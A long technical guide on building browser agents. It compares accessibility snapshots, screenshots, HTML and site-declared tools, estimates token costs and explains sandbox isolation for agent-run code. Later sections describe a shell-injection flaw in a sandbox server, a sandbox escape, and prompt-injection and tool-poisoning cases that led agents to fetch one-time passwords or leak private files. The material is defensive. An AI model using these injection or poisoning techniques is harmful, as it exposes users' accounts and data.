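If the unnamed icon has a ref, the agent may not need the coordinate tools. Calling `browser_snapshot` with `boxes: true` adds each element's position and size to the snapshot. The model can compare these with a screenshot to work out which ref belongs to the icon, then use that ref to click it. This works only if the screenshot and the boxes use the same scale.

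**Custom controls.** Developers sometimes build a checkbox from a script and a plain `<div>`, a general-purpose container. It looks like a checkbox, but without ARIA the snapshot may show only its text. Under the current rule, the agent may still get a ref for the box and be able to click it. But the snapshot won't show whether the box is checked, so the agent may click again to be sure and uncheck it. A screenshot after the first click would show whether the click worked.

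**Menus that open on hover.** Some menus stay hidden until the mouse pointer moves over their heading, and until then their entries are missing from the accessibility tree. The agent may report that the account page has no order history when the link is in a hidden menu. Calling `browser_hover` on the heading opens the menu, and the next snapshot lists the entries.

An element's name in the snapshot is a plain string without markup, so the agent can mistake a crossed-out price for the current one, just as it can in fetched text. It can check the price in the basket or take a screenshot to see which number has a line through it.

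### What "deterministic" means

Playwright calls interaction through snapshots "deterministic" and explains this as "same structure = same interaction". The claim is reasonable if it refers to finding an element from its ref. With a valid ref, the server doesn't have to estimate a button's position from a picture, so moving the button 20 pixels makes no difference. This doesn't establish how snapshots compare with screenshots in measured tests.

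The model still has to choose the ref, and it can choose wrongly. The catalog page with 400 parts may have 400 buttons named "Add", and the model has to pick the one in the row for DP-40. If it picks the button one row down, the server will add a DP-41 to the basket and report no error. The same model may also choose differently when it reads the same page twice.

Small error rates add up over an order. The assistant in the example chooses an element eight times: three fields, the "Check price" button, the "Review order" button twice, the quantity field again and "Place order". If each choice were correct 99 percent of the time and errors were independent, all eight would be correct in about 92 percent of orders. These numbers are illustrative, and real errors are unlikely to be independent, because a confusing page can cause the same mistake on every visit.

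The page can also change between visits without a redesign. A cookie notice, a sale banner or a sold-out item changes the snapshot's structure, so "same structure" may not hold.

A shop that orders the same pump every month can run the routine steps without the model. Version 1.65 of Playwright's Python library can convert a ref an agent has chosen into ordinary code, such as `get_by_role("button", name="Submit")`. A developer can check this code once and then run it for each order. If the supplier renames the button, the script will stop with an error, and the agent can then help find the renamed button.

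## Choosing between snapshots, screenshots, HTML and tools declared by the site

A snapshot is one of four ways to present a page to a model. The assistant could also receive the third supplier's order form as a screenshot, as HTML or, if the supplier's developers have prepared for agents, as a short list of functions.

| | What the model receives | How it acts | What drives the cost | Typical failure |
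|---|---|---|---|---|
| Snapshot | Roles, names, states and refs as text | Names a ref | Number of elements | The markup lacks the element or its name |
| Screenshot | An image of the visible part of the page | Gives x and y coordinates | Image resolution | The click lands beside the target |
| HTML | The page's code, complete or cleaned | Names an element's id or a selector | Amount of code | The model names an element that doesn't exist |
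| Declared tools | Names, descriptions and input schemas | Calls a function | Number of tools and size of results | No tool covers the job |

Some developers draw numbered labels on the screenshot, a method known as set-of-marks, so the model can answer with a number instead of coordinates.

HTML is the bulkiest of the four. *Building Browser Agents* (2025) gives an example in which one form field for a weight takes more than 100 lines of HTML but only a few lines of snapshot. Developers often clean the code first, for instance by removing scripts and styling. The styling can matter, though, because it determines which of two overlapping elements is on top. Playwright MCP has no dedicated tool for HTML, but `browser_evaluate` runs JavaScript on the page and can return the code of one element.

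### How a site declares its own tools

WebMCP is a proposed browser interface that lets a page register functions for agents to call. Its tools have the same parts as ordinary MCP tools, but they run as JavaScript in the page instead of as programs on a server. They therefore use the user's existing login on the site and disappear when the page closes.

The third supplier could declare its price check as follows. The example uses the format of the sample code in Google Chrome Labs' *WebMCP*:

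```
await document.modelContext.registerTool({
  name: "check_price",
  description: "Get stock and trade price for a part.",
  inputSchema: {
    type: "object",
    properties: {
      part: { type: "string" },
      quantity: { type: "integer" }
    },
    required: ["part", "quantity"]
  },
  annotations: { readOnlyHint: true },
  execute: async (input) => await shop.checkPrice(input)
});
```

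*WebMCP*, an unofficial guide to the proposal, divides the process into four steps:

1. The page registers the tool.
2. The agent asks the browser which tools the page offers.
3. The agent sends its arguments, here `{ "part": "DP-40", "quantity": 4 }`.
4. The browser runs the page's function and returns the result, such as a subtotal of $109.60.

This one call replaces filling in two fields, clicking "Check price", waiting and reading a new snapshot. It also avoids the earlier quantity reset, because it sends the part number and the quantity together.

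Chrome for Developers (2026) describes a second method, in which developers annotate an ordinary HTML form and the browser turns it into a tool. It also lists several limits. An agent has to open a page to find out whether it offers tools. By default, the browser doesn't let iframes from other origins register any, so a payment company's embedded card form would normally have none. Google designed the interface mainly for a browser on the user's own computer, with a person present, so it poorly suits a shop that runs its assistant on a server overnight. In its security guidance, Chrome for Developers (2026) also warns that a declared tool's description or results can carry an attack, because they are still text from a website.

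WebMCP is still experimental. Its specification, the Web Machine Learning Community Group's *WebMCP*, has editors from Microsoft and Google, but it is a W3C community group draft and isn't on the W3C standards track. Since version 149, Chrome has run an origin trial, which lets sites sign up to use an unfinished feature with ordinary visitors. Microsoft's Edge has a trial too. According to specification.website's *WebMCP*, earlier drafts used `navigator.modelContext` instead of `document.modelContext`, and portable code checks for both.

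In August 2026, the proposal gained support from both websites and an agent. Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP Connects AI Agents To Actions Inside Websites* reports that Shopify put 10 tools on every storefront built with its Liquid templates. One of them, `proceed_to_checkout`, takes the customer to the checkout but doesn't complete the purchase. On August 25, OpenAI added support to the browser in its ChatGPT desktop app. At launch, the feature required GPT-5.6 Sol or Terra and wasn't available in Enterprise or Edu workspaces, according to Search Engine Journal's *OpenAI Adds WebMCP Site Tools To ChatGPT's Browser*. Chrome for Developers had promised in May that support would come to Gemini in Chrome "soon", in *15 updates from Google I/O 2026*.

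The repair shop should therefore check for declared tools but not depend on them. A supplier on Shopify may have them by default, while one with its own trade portal probably doesn't.

### HTML against the accessibility tree

Developers long assumed that shorter page descriptions were better, partly because early models couldn't handle long inputs. *Read More, Think More* (Enomoto, Obara and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 330 tasks in ServiceNow, a platform for workplace requests. The tasks included ordering items, filling in forms and filtering lists. Each agent had at most 15 steps. Agents always selected elements by their ids, so the researchers could change what the model saw without changing how it acted.

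| Model | Tree | HTML | Tree and screenshot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 52.4% | 67.0% | 53.6% |
| GPT-5.1, high effort | 55.8% | 73.3% | 59.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash, large thinking budget | 45.5% | 56.7% | 48.5% |
| Qwen3-VL-235B Thinking | 45.0% | 39.8% | 44.8% |
| gpt-oss-120b, high effort | 46.7% | 38.8% | No image input |
| gpt-oss-20b, high effort | 46.4% | 27.6% | No image input |
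| Input tokens per step, GPT-5.1 | 6,720 | 56,653 | 7,446 |

The three proprietary models in the table did better with HTML, and the three open models did better with the tree. With HTML, GPT-5.1 and Gemini tried less often to click elements covered by others. Enomoto and colleagues suspect that these models used the styling information to work out which element was on top, but they didn't test this by removing that information. The smallest model in the table, gpt-oss-20b, named nonexistent elements more often when given the longer input.

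The gains were also uneven. Of the 14.6 points that Claude Sonnet 4.6 gained from HTML, 11.8 came from filtering lists, with 39 more successes on 60 tasks. Its score on ordering from a catalog didn't change. GPT-5.1 at high effort lost 1.8 points on forms and gained 0.6 on catalog orders. The pump order is mostly a form, so the shop would pay for about eight times as many input tokens at each step and probably gain nothing. These results come from a single platform, and HTML might help more on a site with worse accessibility markup.

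### Screenshots against text

In 2024, agents in the desktop benchmark OSWorld did better with the accessibility tree than with screenshots alone. This still holds for small models. *TimeWarp* (Ishmam and Marino, 2026) tests agents on an encyclopedia, a news site and a shop, each in six designs that imitate different eras of the web. Qwen-3 VL 8B, a small open model that accepts images, completed 23.0 percent of the tasks with the tree, 24.3 percent with HTML and 0.6 percent with plain screenshots.

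Numbered labels on the screenshots helped this model, but its success rate then varied widely with the design, from 2.6 percent on the worst to 21.4 percent on the best, compared with 19.4 to 27.5 percent for the tree. Ishmam and Marino suggest that a redesign changes a page's appearance more than its underlying structure.

*A11y-Compressor* (2026) reports a similar gap across several kinds of application, with 7.0 percent success for screenshots and 15.6 percent for the tree as text. In one example, both agents failed on a flight-booking page behind a privacy dialog. The agent with the screenshot recognized the dialog but clicked in the wrong places. The agent with the tree failed to detect that the dialog blocked the page and kept trying to use the elements behind it.

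For stronger models, the evidence is less complete. In *ProjGuard* (2026), GPT-5.2 completed 59.0 percent of tasks with screenshots, whether or not it also had the accessibility tree, while Claude Opus 4.5 completed 61.5 percent with screenshots alone and 68.0 percent with both. Neither that test nor the ServiceNow one compares the tree alone with screenshots alone on a strong model. *OS-Omni* (2026), a benchmark that covers several operating systems, uses only screenshots in its main experiments because every platform can supply them, while accessibility trees may be missing or incomplete.

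Adding a screenshot to the tree at every step seems to help only a little. In the ServiceNow test, it raised Claude Sonnet 4.6's score by 1.2 points and that of GPT-5.1 at high effort by 3.9. With 330 tasks, each score has a margin of error of about 5 points, so either gain could be chance. In *It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (2025), Gemini 2.5 Flash completed 13 of 104 runs on a calendar site with the tree alone and 9 of 105 with the screenshot added, which isn't a statistically significant difference either.

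### Declared tools against the browser

No comparable figures exist yet for WebMCP. The closest evidence, from tools that sites offer through ordinary MCP servers, is mixed.

In *MCP vs RAG vs NLWeb vs HTML*, Steiner, Peeters and Bizer (2025) built four simulated shops and gave agents 91 tasks, such as finding the cheapest offer or checking out. The browsing agent, which they call the HTML agent although it reads the accessibility tree, scored 0.67 on F1, a measure that penalizes both wrong and missed answers. The agent with MCP tools scored 0.75. It used 140,000 tokens and took 62 seconds per task, compared with 241,000 tokens and 291 seconds for the browsing agent.

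Part of this difference comes from search. The MCP tools searched by meaning, while the browsing agent used each shop's own search box. The scores were almost equal on finding the cheapest product, which is the repair shop's job, with 0.61 for browsing and 0.63 for MCP. The result also depended on the model. GPT-4.1 completed every cart and checkout task by browsing but only 73 percent with the tools, while GPT-5 completed 67 percent by browsing and 93 percent with the tools.

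*Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation* (Bechard, Marquez Ayala and colleagues, 2026) reports nearly the opposite result on 729 tasks across three business platforms. Claude Opus 4.6 completed 79.9 percent of the tasks through Playwright MCP, at $3.97 per task, and 39.2 percent through publicly available MCP servers for the platforms, at $0.58 per task. The servers often lacked the action a task required. In one run, an agent found an iPad in the catalog but had no tool for ordering it, so it filed a support ticket instead. The gap in completion rate was smallest on the platform whose server had only seven tools, because those tools could create or change any kind of record.

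WebMCP could have the same problem. A site's developers may declare search and checkout but leave out returns, so an agent that has to send back a faulty pump will still need the ordinary page.

### What the tool makers claim

Playwright's documentation rates snapshots above screenshots on token use, precision, speed and reliability, without giving measurements. The tests on small models support the claim about precision, but the claim about token use is doubtful. In the ServiceNow test, GPT-5.1's prompt averaged 6,720 tokens with the tree, and adding a screenshot raised that by only 726 tokens per step.

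The number of tokens a screenshot takes depends on its resolution and on how the provider counts images, not on how many elements it shows. The earlier catalog page with 400 parts takes about 20,000 tokens as a snapshot and would take far fewer as a screenshot, but the screenshot would show only the rows on the screen. The short order form probably takes fewer tokens as a snapshot.

Google Chrome Labs claims that WebMCP is faster and more secure and uses fewer tokens. It illustrates this with a booking widget that an agent can control through three tools instead of more than 40 page elements. The example makes lower token use plausible for that widget, but it doesn't test agents on real sites.

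### What a task costs in tokens

Suppose the instructions and tool definitions take *b* tokens, each snapshot takes *s* tokens and every snapshot stays in the context, which the model rereads before each action. At step *k*, the model reads *b* + *ks* tokens. Over *n* steps, the total is:

```
total = n·b + s·n(n + 1)/2
```

An order that takes 12 steps, with 5,000 tokens of instructions and 3,000 per snapshot, uses 60,000 + 234,000 = 294,000 tokens. If each step adds only 400 tokens, perhaps because the agent uses `browser_find` or a declared tool, the total falls to 91,200. Long tasks use disproportionately more tokens because the second term grows with the square of the number of steps. With 24 steps and full snapshots, the total is 1,020,000 tokens, about three and a half times as many as with 12.

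Many providers discount recently processed text, a feature known as prompt caching. The discount applies only up to the first point where a new request differs from the earlier one, so removing an old snapshot returns everything after it to full price.

The next table applies this to the 12-step order, assuming that cached tokens cost a tenth of the normal price. It excludes the model's output and any charge for storing the cache.

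| Snapshots the host keeps | Tokens read | Cost with caching, in full-price tokens |
|---|---|---|
| All | 294,000 | 66,300 |
| The last four | 186,000 | 120,300 |
| Only the latest | 96,000 | 46,500 |

Without caching, keeping fewer snapshots always saves money. With caching, keeping the last four costs almost twice as much as keeping all of them, because from the fifth step on, the host removes a snapshot near the start of the history at every step. Keeping only the latest is still the cheapest, since the removed snapshot is always at the end of the previous request. But caching doesn't free space in the model's context, so a long task can still fill it.

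Old snapshots have some value. Enomoto and colleagues found that GPT-5.1 at high effort succeeded on 55.8 percent of tasks when it saw only the current page and on 58.8 percent when it also saw the previous nine. Sending only the differences between those pages gave the same 58.8 percent and cut the input from 39,011 to 13,670 tokens per step. The 3-point gain is within the margin of error, but most other models also improved with some history. They also repeated their previous action less often, which reduces the risk of errors such as placing the same order twice.

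### Controlling the browser from the command line

Agents that can run shell commands can use Playwright's command-line tool instead of its MCP server. The command `playwright-cli snapshot` writes the snapshot to a file, which the agent can search for the part it needs. The agent then acts with a command such as `playwright-cli fill e20 "4"`.

According to Playwright, which gives no figures, the command line uses fewer tokens than the MCP server because tool definitions and snapshots stay out of the context and the agent loads instructions only when it needs them. Playwright recommends the command line for coding agents that work with large codebases, and the MCP server for exploring sites and for specialized agents. In the formula, the command line reduces both *b* and *s*. If they fell to 2,000 and 400, the 12-step order would take 55,200 tokens. An agent that prints the whole snapshot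 file after every click would lose most of that saving.

Bechard and colleagues also tested agents that skipped the browser and used a terminal to call the platforms' programming interfaces directly. Claude Opus 4.6 completed 78.7 percent of the tasks this way at $1.22 per task, roughly matching the browser for less than a third of the cost. The result is a good reason to ask a supplier whether it has such an interface, but it doesn't measure Playwright's command-line tool.

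The command line also requires more trust, because an agent with a shell can run other programs and so needs a sandbox. By default, the command-line tool runs the browser without a visible window, while the MCP server shows one. With the command-line tool, the owner of the repair shop wouldn't see the order form unless somebody changed that setting.

### Starting with a snapshot and adding a screenshot

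For most sites, the agent should start with a snapshot and take a screenshot where the tree has gaps. It should also take one if the tool returns success for a click but the snapshot doesn't change, since a pop-up may be covering the page. In the flight-booking example, a screenshot could have shown the dialog, and a ref could have identified the exact button to click.

The deployer should test whether the model follows such a rule. Bechard and colleagues gave agents both a terminal and a browser and told them to prefer the terminal for working with data. On ServiceNow, Claude Sonnet 4.6 still made 82 percent of its tool calls through the browser. Across all three platforms, it completed 72.0 percent of the tasks with both tools, no better than with the terminal alone. Claude Opus 4.6 completed 81.4 percent with both, slightly better than with the terminal alone.

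The table gives a starting point for each type of page.

| Type of page | Start with | When to switch |
|---|---|---|
| Public page that the agent only has to read | Fetch tool | Use a snapshot if a script loads the price |
| Labeled form, such as the pump order | Snapshot | Take a screenshot if a click has no effect |
| Long catalog or list | `browser_find` or a partial snapshot | Try the list's HTML with a strong model if filtering keeps failing |
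| Page behind a pop-up | Snapshot and screenshot, then click by ref | Use coordinates if the pop-up's button has no ref |
| Buttons with unnamed icons | Screenshot and a snapshot with `boxes: true` | Use coordinates if the icon has no ref |
| Canvas, map or part diagram | Screenshot with coordinates | Return to snapshots once ordinary page content opens |
| Site with WebMCP tools, in a browser and agent that support them | Declared tool | Use a snapshot if no tool covers the job |

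## Running code in a sandbox

The third supplier's price list is a file, so the assistant can process it with a program. If the list has 4,000 rows of about 60 characters each, reading it would add about 60,000 tokens to the context, and the model could still pick the wrong row or get the arithmetic wrong. If a program processes the list instead, the model only has to read the answer.

Agents run code for three purposes, and the code needs different access for each:

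- To compute on data the agent already has, a program needs the data file and nothing else.
- To call other MCP tools and pass results between them, a program needs access to those tools.
- To do something in the browser that the ordinary tools can't, code runs in the web page or in the browser server, where the shop's login is within reach.

### Calling tools from a script

Normally, every tool result passes through the model. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP*, an article from November 2025, gives the example of an agent that downloads a meeting transcript from Google Drive and attaches it to a customer record in Salesforce. The model reads the transcript in the result of the first tool call, then writes it all out again as an argument to the second. For a two-hour meeting, this could add 50,000 tokens, and the model may make mistakes when copying the text.

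Anthropic suggests presenting each tool as a code file in a folder. The agent lists the folder, reads the files for the tools it needs and writes a script that passes the transcript straight from one tool to the other. Anthropic says this cuts token use from 150,000 to 2,000. It attributes the saving to loading tool definitions on demand but doesn't say which tools it counted or how. A saving that large can only apply to an agent with a very large number of tools. The shop's assistant, with the 5,000 tokens of instructions and definitions assumed earlier, would save far fewer tokens by loading definitions on demand.

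Cloudflare, a company that hosts and protects websites, had described a similar method that September. Varda and Pai, in *Code Mode*, explain how it works:

1. The agent's software converts the tool definitions into a programming interface in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript.
2. The model receives this interface and a single tool that runs code.
3. The model's program runs in an isolate, a small separate JavaScript runtime that starts in a few milliseconds and has no internet access.
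4. When the program calls an MCP tool, the call goes back to the agent's software, which adds the access key and contacts the server.
5. The model gets back only what the program prints.

Varda and Pai report that agents handle more tools this way, perhaps because models have seen far more real code than tool calls in training, but they give no measurements. Their first version still loaded the whole interface into the context, so it saved tokens on intermediate results but not on tool definitions.

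A later Cloudflare server, which Carey describes in *Code Mode*, an article with the same main title, also uses fewer tokens for tool definitions. Its two tools, `search` and `execute`, cover more than 2,500 operations on Cloudflare's platform, and their definitions take about 1,000 tokens. Carey reports that this is 99.9 percent less than the 1.17 million tokens a server with one tool per operation would need. But Carey also says those 1.17 million tokens wouldn't fit in the context of the most advanced models, so the larger server isn't a realistic alternative. The comparison also leaves out the programs the model writes and the search results it reads.

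AIMultiple, a consultancy, compared the two methods on agents that did the same work. Code execution used 165,000 input tokens instead of 771,000, but 2.2 times as many output tokens, which usually cost more. The totals imply roughly 10,000 output tokens instead of 4,000. If output tokens cost five times as much as input tokens, code execution would still be about 73 percent cheaper. Prompt caching would probably reduce this saving further, because every request starts with the same tool definitions.

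Scripts work less well when a result should change what the agent does next. In the pump order, a script that clicked through to the end would probably have missed the reset quantity and ordered one pump. Scripts are better for reading and transferring data, but clicks that change an order should remain separate calls.

Where the script runs also affects how much control the host has. In Varda and Pai's design, each tool call passes through the agent's software, which can stop it. With Carey's server, the client doesn't need a sandbox, but it receives only one call to `execute` containing a whole program, so approving that call means approving everything the program does. Cloudflare's *Code mode for MCP server portals* (2026) says code mode is on by default in its portals, which combine several MCP servers behind one address, so deployers who use them should check this setting.

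### Four levels of isolation

Programs use system calls to request files, memory and network connections from the kernel, the core of the operating system. The usual methods of isolating code differ mainly in how much of the machine's kernel the code can reach. The table lists these methods roughly from weakest to strongest.

| Level | What it shares with the machine | What a flaw exposes |
|---|---|---|
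| Restricted language runtime | The kernel, and sometimes the process of the application that uses it | Whatever that process can access |
| Container | The kernel | The whole machine, including other containers |
| Container with a user-space kernel | The hardware and a small part of the kernel's interface | The user-space kernel, and the machine only if the attacker finds a second flaw |
| Virtual machine | The hardware, through a hypervisor | The machine, if the flaw is in the hypervisor or its supporting software |

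A restricted language runtime leaves out the operations that could do damage. Monty, a Python interpreter for code written by models, can't open a file or a network connection by itself. According to Pydantic's *Security Model* for Monty, a program can reach only the folders, functions and objects that the deployer supplies. In one example, a program uses a supplied function called `get_price` to look up an item and double its price. Supplied functions run with the full rights of the application that supplies them. If one of them can fetch any web address, the program has internet access.

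In 2026, Pydantic offered $5,000 to anyone who could break out of Monty and read a secret. Hewitt (2026) reports in *Hack Monty* that a researcher succeeded in less than 48 hours. The researcher combined two memory-management bugs to run code outside the interpreter's restrictions. Pydantic fixed the hole in version 0.0.16. Hewitt considers it a good sign that more than a million requests turned up only one such hole, but one was enough to get the secret, and the number of requests is weak evidence of the attackers' skill.

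A container uses features of the Linux kernel to limit which files, processes and networks a program can access. All containers on a machine use the same kernel, so a program that exploits a kernel bug can take over the machine. Filters can block some system calls, but a filter that suits most programs has to allow most of the kernel's functions. gVisor, a project that builds a stronger kind of container, describes a program isolated only by these kernel features as "only one system call away from host compromise".

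gVisor puts a second kernel between the program and the machine's own. This kernel runs as an ordinary application, which is why engineers call it a user-space kernel. If a program asks for its process number, gVisor answers from its own table without asking the real kernel. Some requests do lead to calls to the real kernel, but gVisor makes those itself and never passes the program's calls through. To break out, an attacker has to exploit both kernels, which share no code. The cost is compatibility, since a program can't use kernel features that gVisor hasn't reimplemented. Deployers should also avoid judging its file protection by the quick test command `runsc do`, which lets the program read the machine's entire filesystem by default.

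A virtual machine has its own complete kernel and runs on simulated hardware. A hypervisor manages it and controls its access to the real machine. *Firecracker* (2020), a paper on a lightweight virtual machine system, argues that virtualization moves the security-critical boundary from the operating system to hardware and comparatively simple software. Virtual machines usually need more memory than containers, but *Firecracker* reports a memory overhead of less than 5 MB per virtual machine with a minimal kernel.

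gVisor's *Security Model* disputes that virtual machines are automatically safer, because the software that simulates their devices can be complex and often runs without a sandbox. gVisor's developers have their own product to defend, but Firecracker's design supports their point. Its developers replaced QEMU, a general-purpose program with more than 1.4 million lines of code, partly because QEMU's priority was flexibility and not security.

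### When the server is the weak point

The software that starts a sandbox can fail even if the sandbox works as intended. The MCP server `node-code-sandbox-mcp` ran JavaScript in Docker, a widely used container system. It started the containers by inserting the caller's input into a shell command. A shell treats certain characters as instructions, so crafted input could add a second command. That command ran on the host machine, outside Docker, with the server's privileges, as GitLab's *CVE-2025-53372* (2025) explains.

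Version 1.3.0 fixed the flaw. GCVE's *GHSA-5w57-2ccq-8w95* recommends passing the arguments to the program as a separate list, so that no shell interprets them. Deployers should treat the server that starts the sandbox as part of the sandbox, keeping it up to date and giving it few privileges.

Some unsafe servers are never fixed. `mcp-run-python` ran a model's Python code in the same JavaScript environment as the server. JFrog's *JFSA-2026-001653030* (2026) reports that the code could change the server, including the tools it offered. According to the notice in Glama's *MCP Run Python*, the maintainers archived the project after concluding that they couldn't make this design both safe and fast enough. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2628* advises users to stop using it immediately.

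### The network setting

A program with unrestricted internet access can send out everything it can read, even from a virtual machine that nobody can break out of. Isolation and network access are separate settings. By default, a program in gVisor can make network connections much as it could in an ordinary container, so the deployer has to restrict them.

The archived Python server had a second flaw, which was that it gave sandboxed code too much network access. According to MagicSlides' *Python Sandbox* (2025), a copy of the server's instructions, the server required network access to download Python's standard library and packages. GitLab reports that this permission also covered localhost, the address programs use to connect to other programs on the same machine. Code in the sandbox could therefore send requests to databases and other internal services on that machine.

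Deployers can restrict which servers code in a sandbox may contact. The options include a package mirror, which is a server that holds copies of software packages, and an allowlist, which names the addresses a program may contact.

| Setting | What the program can do | What can still leave the sandbox |
|---|---|---|
| No network | Use supplied files and installed packages | Only the output |
| Package mirror only | Also install packages from the mirror | The output, and data hidden in package requests if the mirror forwards them |
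| Allowlist | Also contact the approved addresses | Anything those addresses accept |

Code in a sandbox without network access fails if it needs a package that isn't installed. Giving the sandbox access to a package mirror solves this, but packages can contain harmful code. If the mirror looks up unknown names in a public registry, that code could send data out by, for example, requesting a package whose name contains a customer's phone number. A mirror limited to a fixed set of packages prevents this.

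A program that has to fetch live data needs an allowlist of approved addresses. The risk depends on what each address accepts, since a program can upload files to an approved file-sharing site as easily as it can download them. Deno's *Security* describes a service that keeps the real access key outside the sandbox and inserts it only into requests to an approved address. The program can't print the key, but it can still do anything the key permits at that address.

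Varda and Pai prefer to give a program specific functions instead of network access, because it's often unclear which traffic a filter should allow. This is a good argument when the functions are narrow. For the repair shop, it's simpler to install the packages beforehand, have another tool download the price list and run the calculation with no network. The browser and the fetch tool still have network connections, which need separate rules.

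### Code in the page and code in the browser server

Playwright MCP has two tools for running JavaScript. `browser_evaluate` runs it inside the web page, and `browser_run_code_unsafe` runs it in the server process that controls the browser. Playwright's *Code Execution* calls the second tool "RCE-equivalent". RCE, or remote code execution, means that someone can run any program on another person's machine.

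Code in the page must follow the browser's rules. It can't freely read the machine's files, and the same-origin policy keeps it out of a payment company's embedded form. But it can still do harm. Because the browser is logged in to the third supplier's site, the code can read the shop's trade prices and submit an order there.

Code in the server process can do whatever the server's user account permits, such as reading files or starting other programs. It also controls the browser from outside the page. In Playwright's examples, such code reads the total from a payment form in an iframe and gives a site permission to use the clipboard. The server's restrictions on websites and files won't reliably contain it, and Playwright's *Configuration* describes them as conveniences, not a security boundary.

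Playwright advises enabling the unsafe tool only for trusted MCP clients, but lists it among the core tools that are always enabled. Trusting the client isn't enough, because even a trustworthy client passes on code from a model that has just read a supplier's website. The deployer should remove the tool in the host and run the browser server in a container without the shop's files.

The tool's earlier name was `browser_run_code`, and Glama's *browser_run_code* shows a description without the warning. A rule that blocks only the old name won't block the tool under its new name, so a list of permitted tools is safer than a list of forbidden ones. The unsafe tool accepts code either as text or from a file, and if a call includes both, it ignores the text. If the approval prompt shows only the text, the owner could approve code that won't run.

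The shop doesn't need this tool. Playwright suggests it for uses such as iframes and unusual waiting conditions, but the assistant can use ordinary refs inside an iframe and wait for text with `browser_wait_for`.

### Calculating the cost of the pumps

Suppose the price list is a CSV file, a plain-text table, with columns for the part number, the minimum quantity and the unit price. DP-40 costs $27.40 each, or $25.90 each for orders of ten or more. The supplier charges $9.50 for shipping on orders under $120, and the shop pays 8 percent tax on the goods and shipping. The assistant writes this program:

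```
import csv, json
from decimal import Decimal as D

part, qty = "DP-40", 4
with open("/data/prices.csv", newline="") as f:
    rows = [r for r in csv.DictReader(f)
            if r["part"] == part and int(r["min_qty"]) <= qty]

tier = max((int(r["min_qty"]) for r in rows), default=0)
prices = {r["unit_price"] for r in rows
          if int(r["min_qty"]) == tier}
if len(prices) != 1:
    raise ValueError("No single price found")

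unit = D(prices.pop())
goods = unit * qty
shipping = D("0.00") if goods >= 120 else D("9.50")
total = round((goods + shipping) * D("1.08"), 2)
print(json.dumps({"part": part, "quantity": qty,
    "unit": str(unit), "goods": str(goods),
    "shipping": str(shipping), "total": str(total)}))
```

The program looks for an exact part number, so it can't pick DP-400 by mistake. It then chooses the highest quantity tier that the order reaches. Four pumps don't qualify for the discount, so the goods cost 4 × $27.40 = $109.60. Shipping brings this to $119.10, and tax brings it to $128.63. If the list contains no price for the part, or two different prices for the same tier, the program stops without calculating a total.

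The host saves the program and the price list in a folder for this job and runs them with gVisor:

```
docker run --rm --runtime=runsc --network=none \
  --read-only --memory=256m --cpus=1 --pids-limit=32 \
  --user=65534 -v /srv/jobs/417:/data:ro \
  python:3.13-slim python /data/job.py
```

The program can read the job folder but can't change it. It has no network access, at most 256 MB of memory and one processor core, and it receives neither the supplier's password nor the browser's cookies. The command sets no time limit, so the host has to stop the container if it is still running after, say, 10 seconds. Python's standard library is enough for a CSV file. An Excel file would need an extra package, which the deployer can add to the container image beforehand.

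The host should accept only one output of at most 500 characters, with exactly these six fields:

```
{"part": "DP-40", "quantity": 4, "unit": "27.40",
 "goods": "109.60", "shipping": "9.50", "total": "128.63"}
```

Before passing the result to the model, the host checks that the part and quantity match the owner's request and that the other four values are plain numbers. This keeps the rest of the list out of the context, including any instructions hidden in a product description. If a cell in the quantity column contains text instead of a number, Python's error message quotes that text, so the host should also replace the error message with a fixed one such as "Calculation failed".

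Even with these limits, the answer can be wrong, because the model may have misread the shipping terms or the list may be out of date. If the subtotal on the order form isn't $109.60, the assistant should stop and tell the owner.

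## How a web page can give an agent instructions

During an order, the repair shop's assistant mostly reads text written by other people, such as search excerpts, product pages and a price list. Any of these texts can carry an indirect prompt injection. The attacker only has to get text into the agent's context and doesn't need a flaw in the browser, the sandbox or the server.

### One sequence of tokens

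A sandbox server like the flawed one in the previous section can keep an attacker's text out of the command by passing it as a separate argument. A language model has no separate channel of this kind. The host joins the owner's request, the tool definitions and the tool results into one sequence of tokens, and the model computes its next output from the whole sequence:

```
p(next action | text before + attacker's text + text after)
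```

The attacker controls only the middle part, but the probability of every possible action depends on it. *Are AI-assisted Development Tools Immune to Prompt Injection?* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026) calls the flaw structural, because models can't perfectly distinguish instructions from data.

Hosts use special tokens to mark where the user's message ends and a tool result begins. Some developers also train their models to give tool results the lowest priority, an approach known as an instruction hierarchy. This training only makes the model tend to follow that priority, and no software enforces it. Attackers can also imitate the tokens in retrieved text so that the model misidentifies the source of the text, as *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes.

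A model has to follow some of the instructions it finds on a page. If the third supplier's form says to enter part numbers without the hyphen, the assistant should do so. It has to judge which instructions serve the owner's request, and an attacker can write one that appears to serve it.

Greshake and colleagues gave the first full account of the problem in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). One of their tests used a simulated search engine that ran on GPT-4. An instruction in the middle of a full Wikipedia article led the model to search for a code word. The search result contained a second set of instructions, so the attacker needed only a small space on the first page.

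### The routes into the context

Every tool that returns text is a possible route. The routes differ in who can write the text and when the model reads it.

| Route | Who can write the text | When the model reads it |
|---|---|---|
| Search excerpt | The owner of any page that ranks for the query | Before it chooses a page |
| Fetched page | The site's owner | After the fetch |
| Snapshot | The site's owner, and advertisers or others with an iframe on the page | After most browser actions |
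| Comment, review or listing | Any user who may post on the site | With the page that contains it |
| MCP tool description | The developer of the server | Before it opens any page |
| WebMCP declaration | The site's owner, or a script the site includes | When the browser lists the page's tools |

Comments are a particular problem because the site itself may be trustworthy. The shop could approve three reputable suppliers and still receive an attack from a customer review at one of them. According to The Decoder's *Perplexity's BrowseSafe tries to patch the gaping security holes*, Brave discovered in August 2025 that commands hidden in pages or comments could steer the assistant in Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, when the user merely asked for a summary. *In-Browser LLM-Guided Fuzzing for Real-Time Prompt Injection Testing in Agentic AI Browsers* (2025) mentions a Reddit comment that carried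 the commands, and *Building Browser Agents* reports that the assistant went on to fetch one-time passwords from the user's email.

When the fetch tool converts a page to Markdown, it discards the styling, so white text on a white background can look the same to the model as the product description around it.

A WebMCP declaration can add risk even though it comes from the same site as the page. It reaches the model as a tool definition, which the model has to rely on to use the tool.

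### Poisoned tool descriptions

The same reliance makes ordinary MCP tools a target. In tool poisoning, the attacker puts instructions in a tool's description or input schema, and the tool's code can be harmless. For instance, a free unit-conversion server could describe an extra argument in a way that leads the model to fill it with the contents of a private file, while the owner sees a request to convert inches to millimeters.

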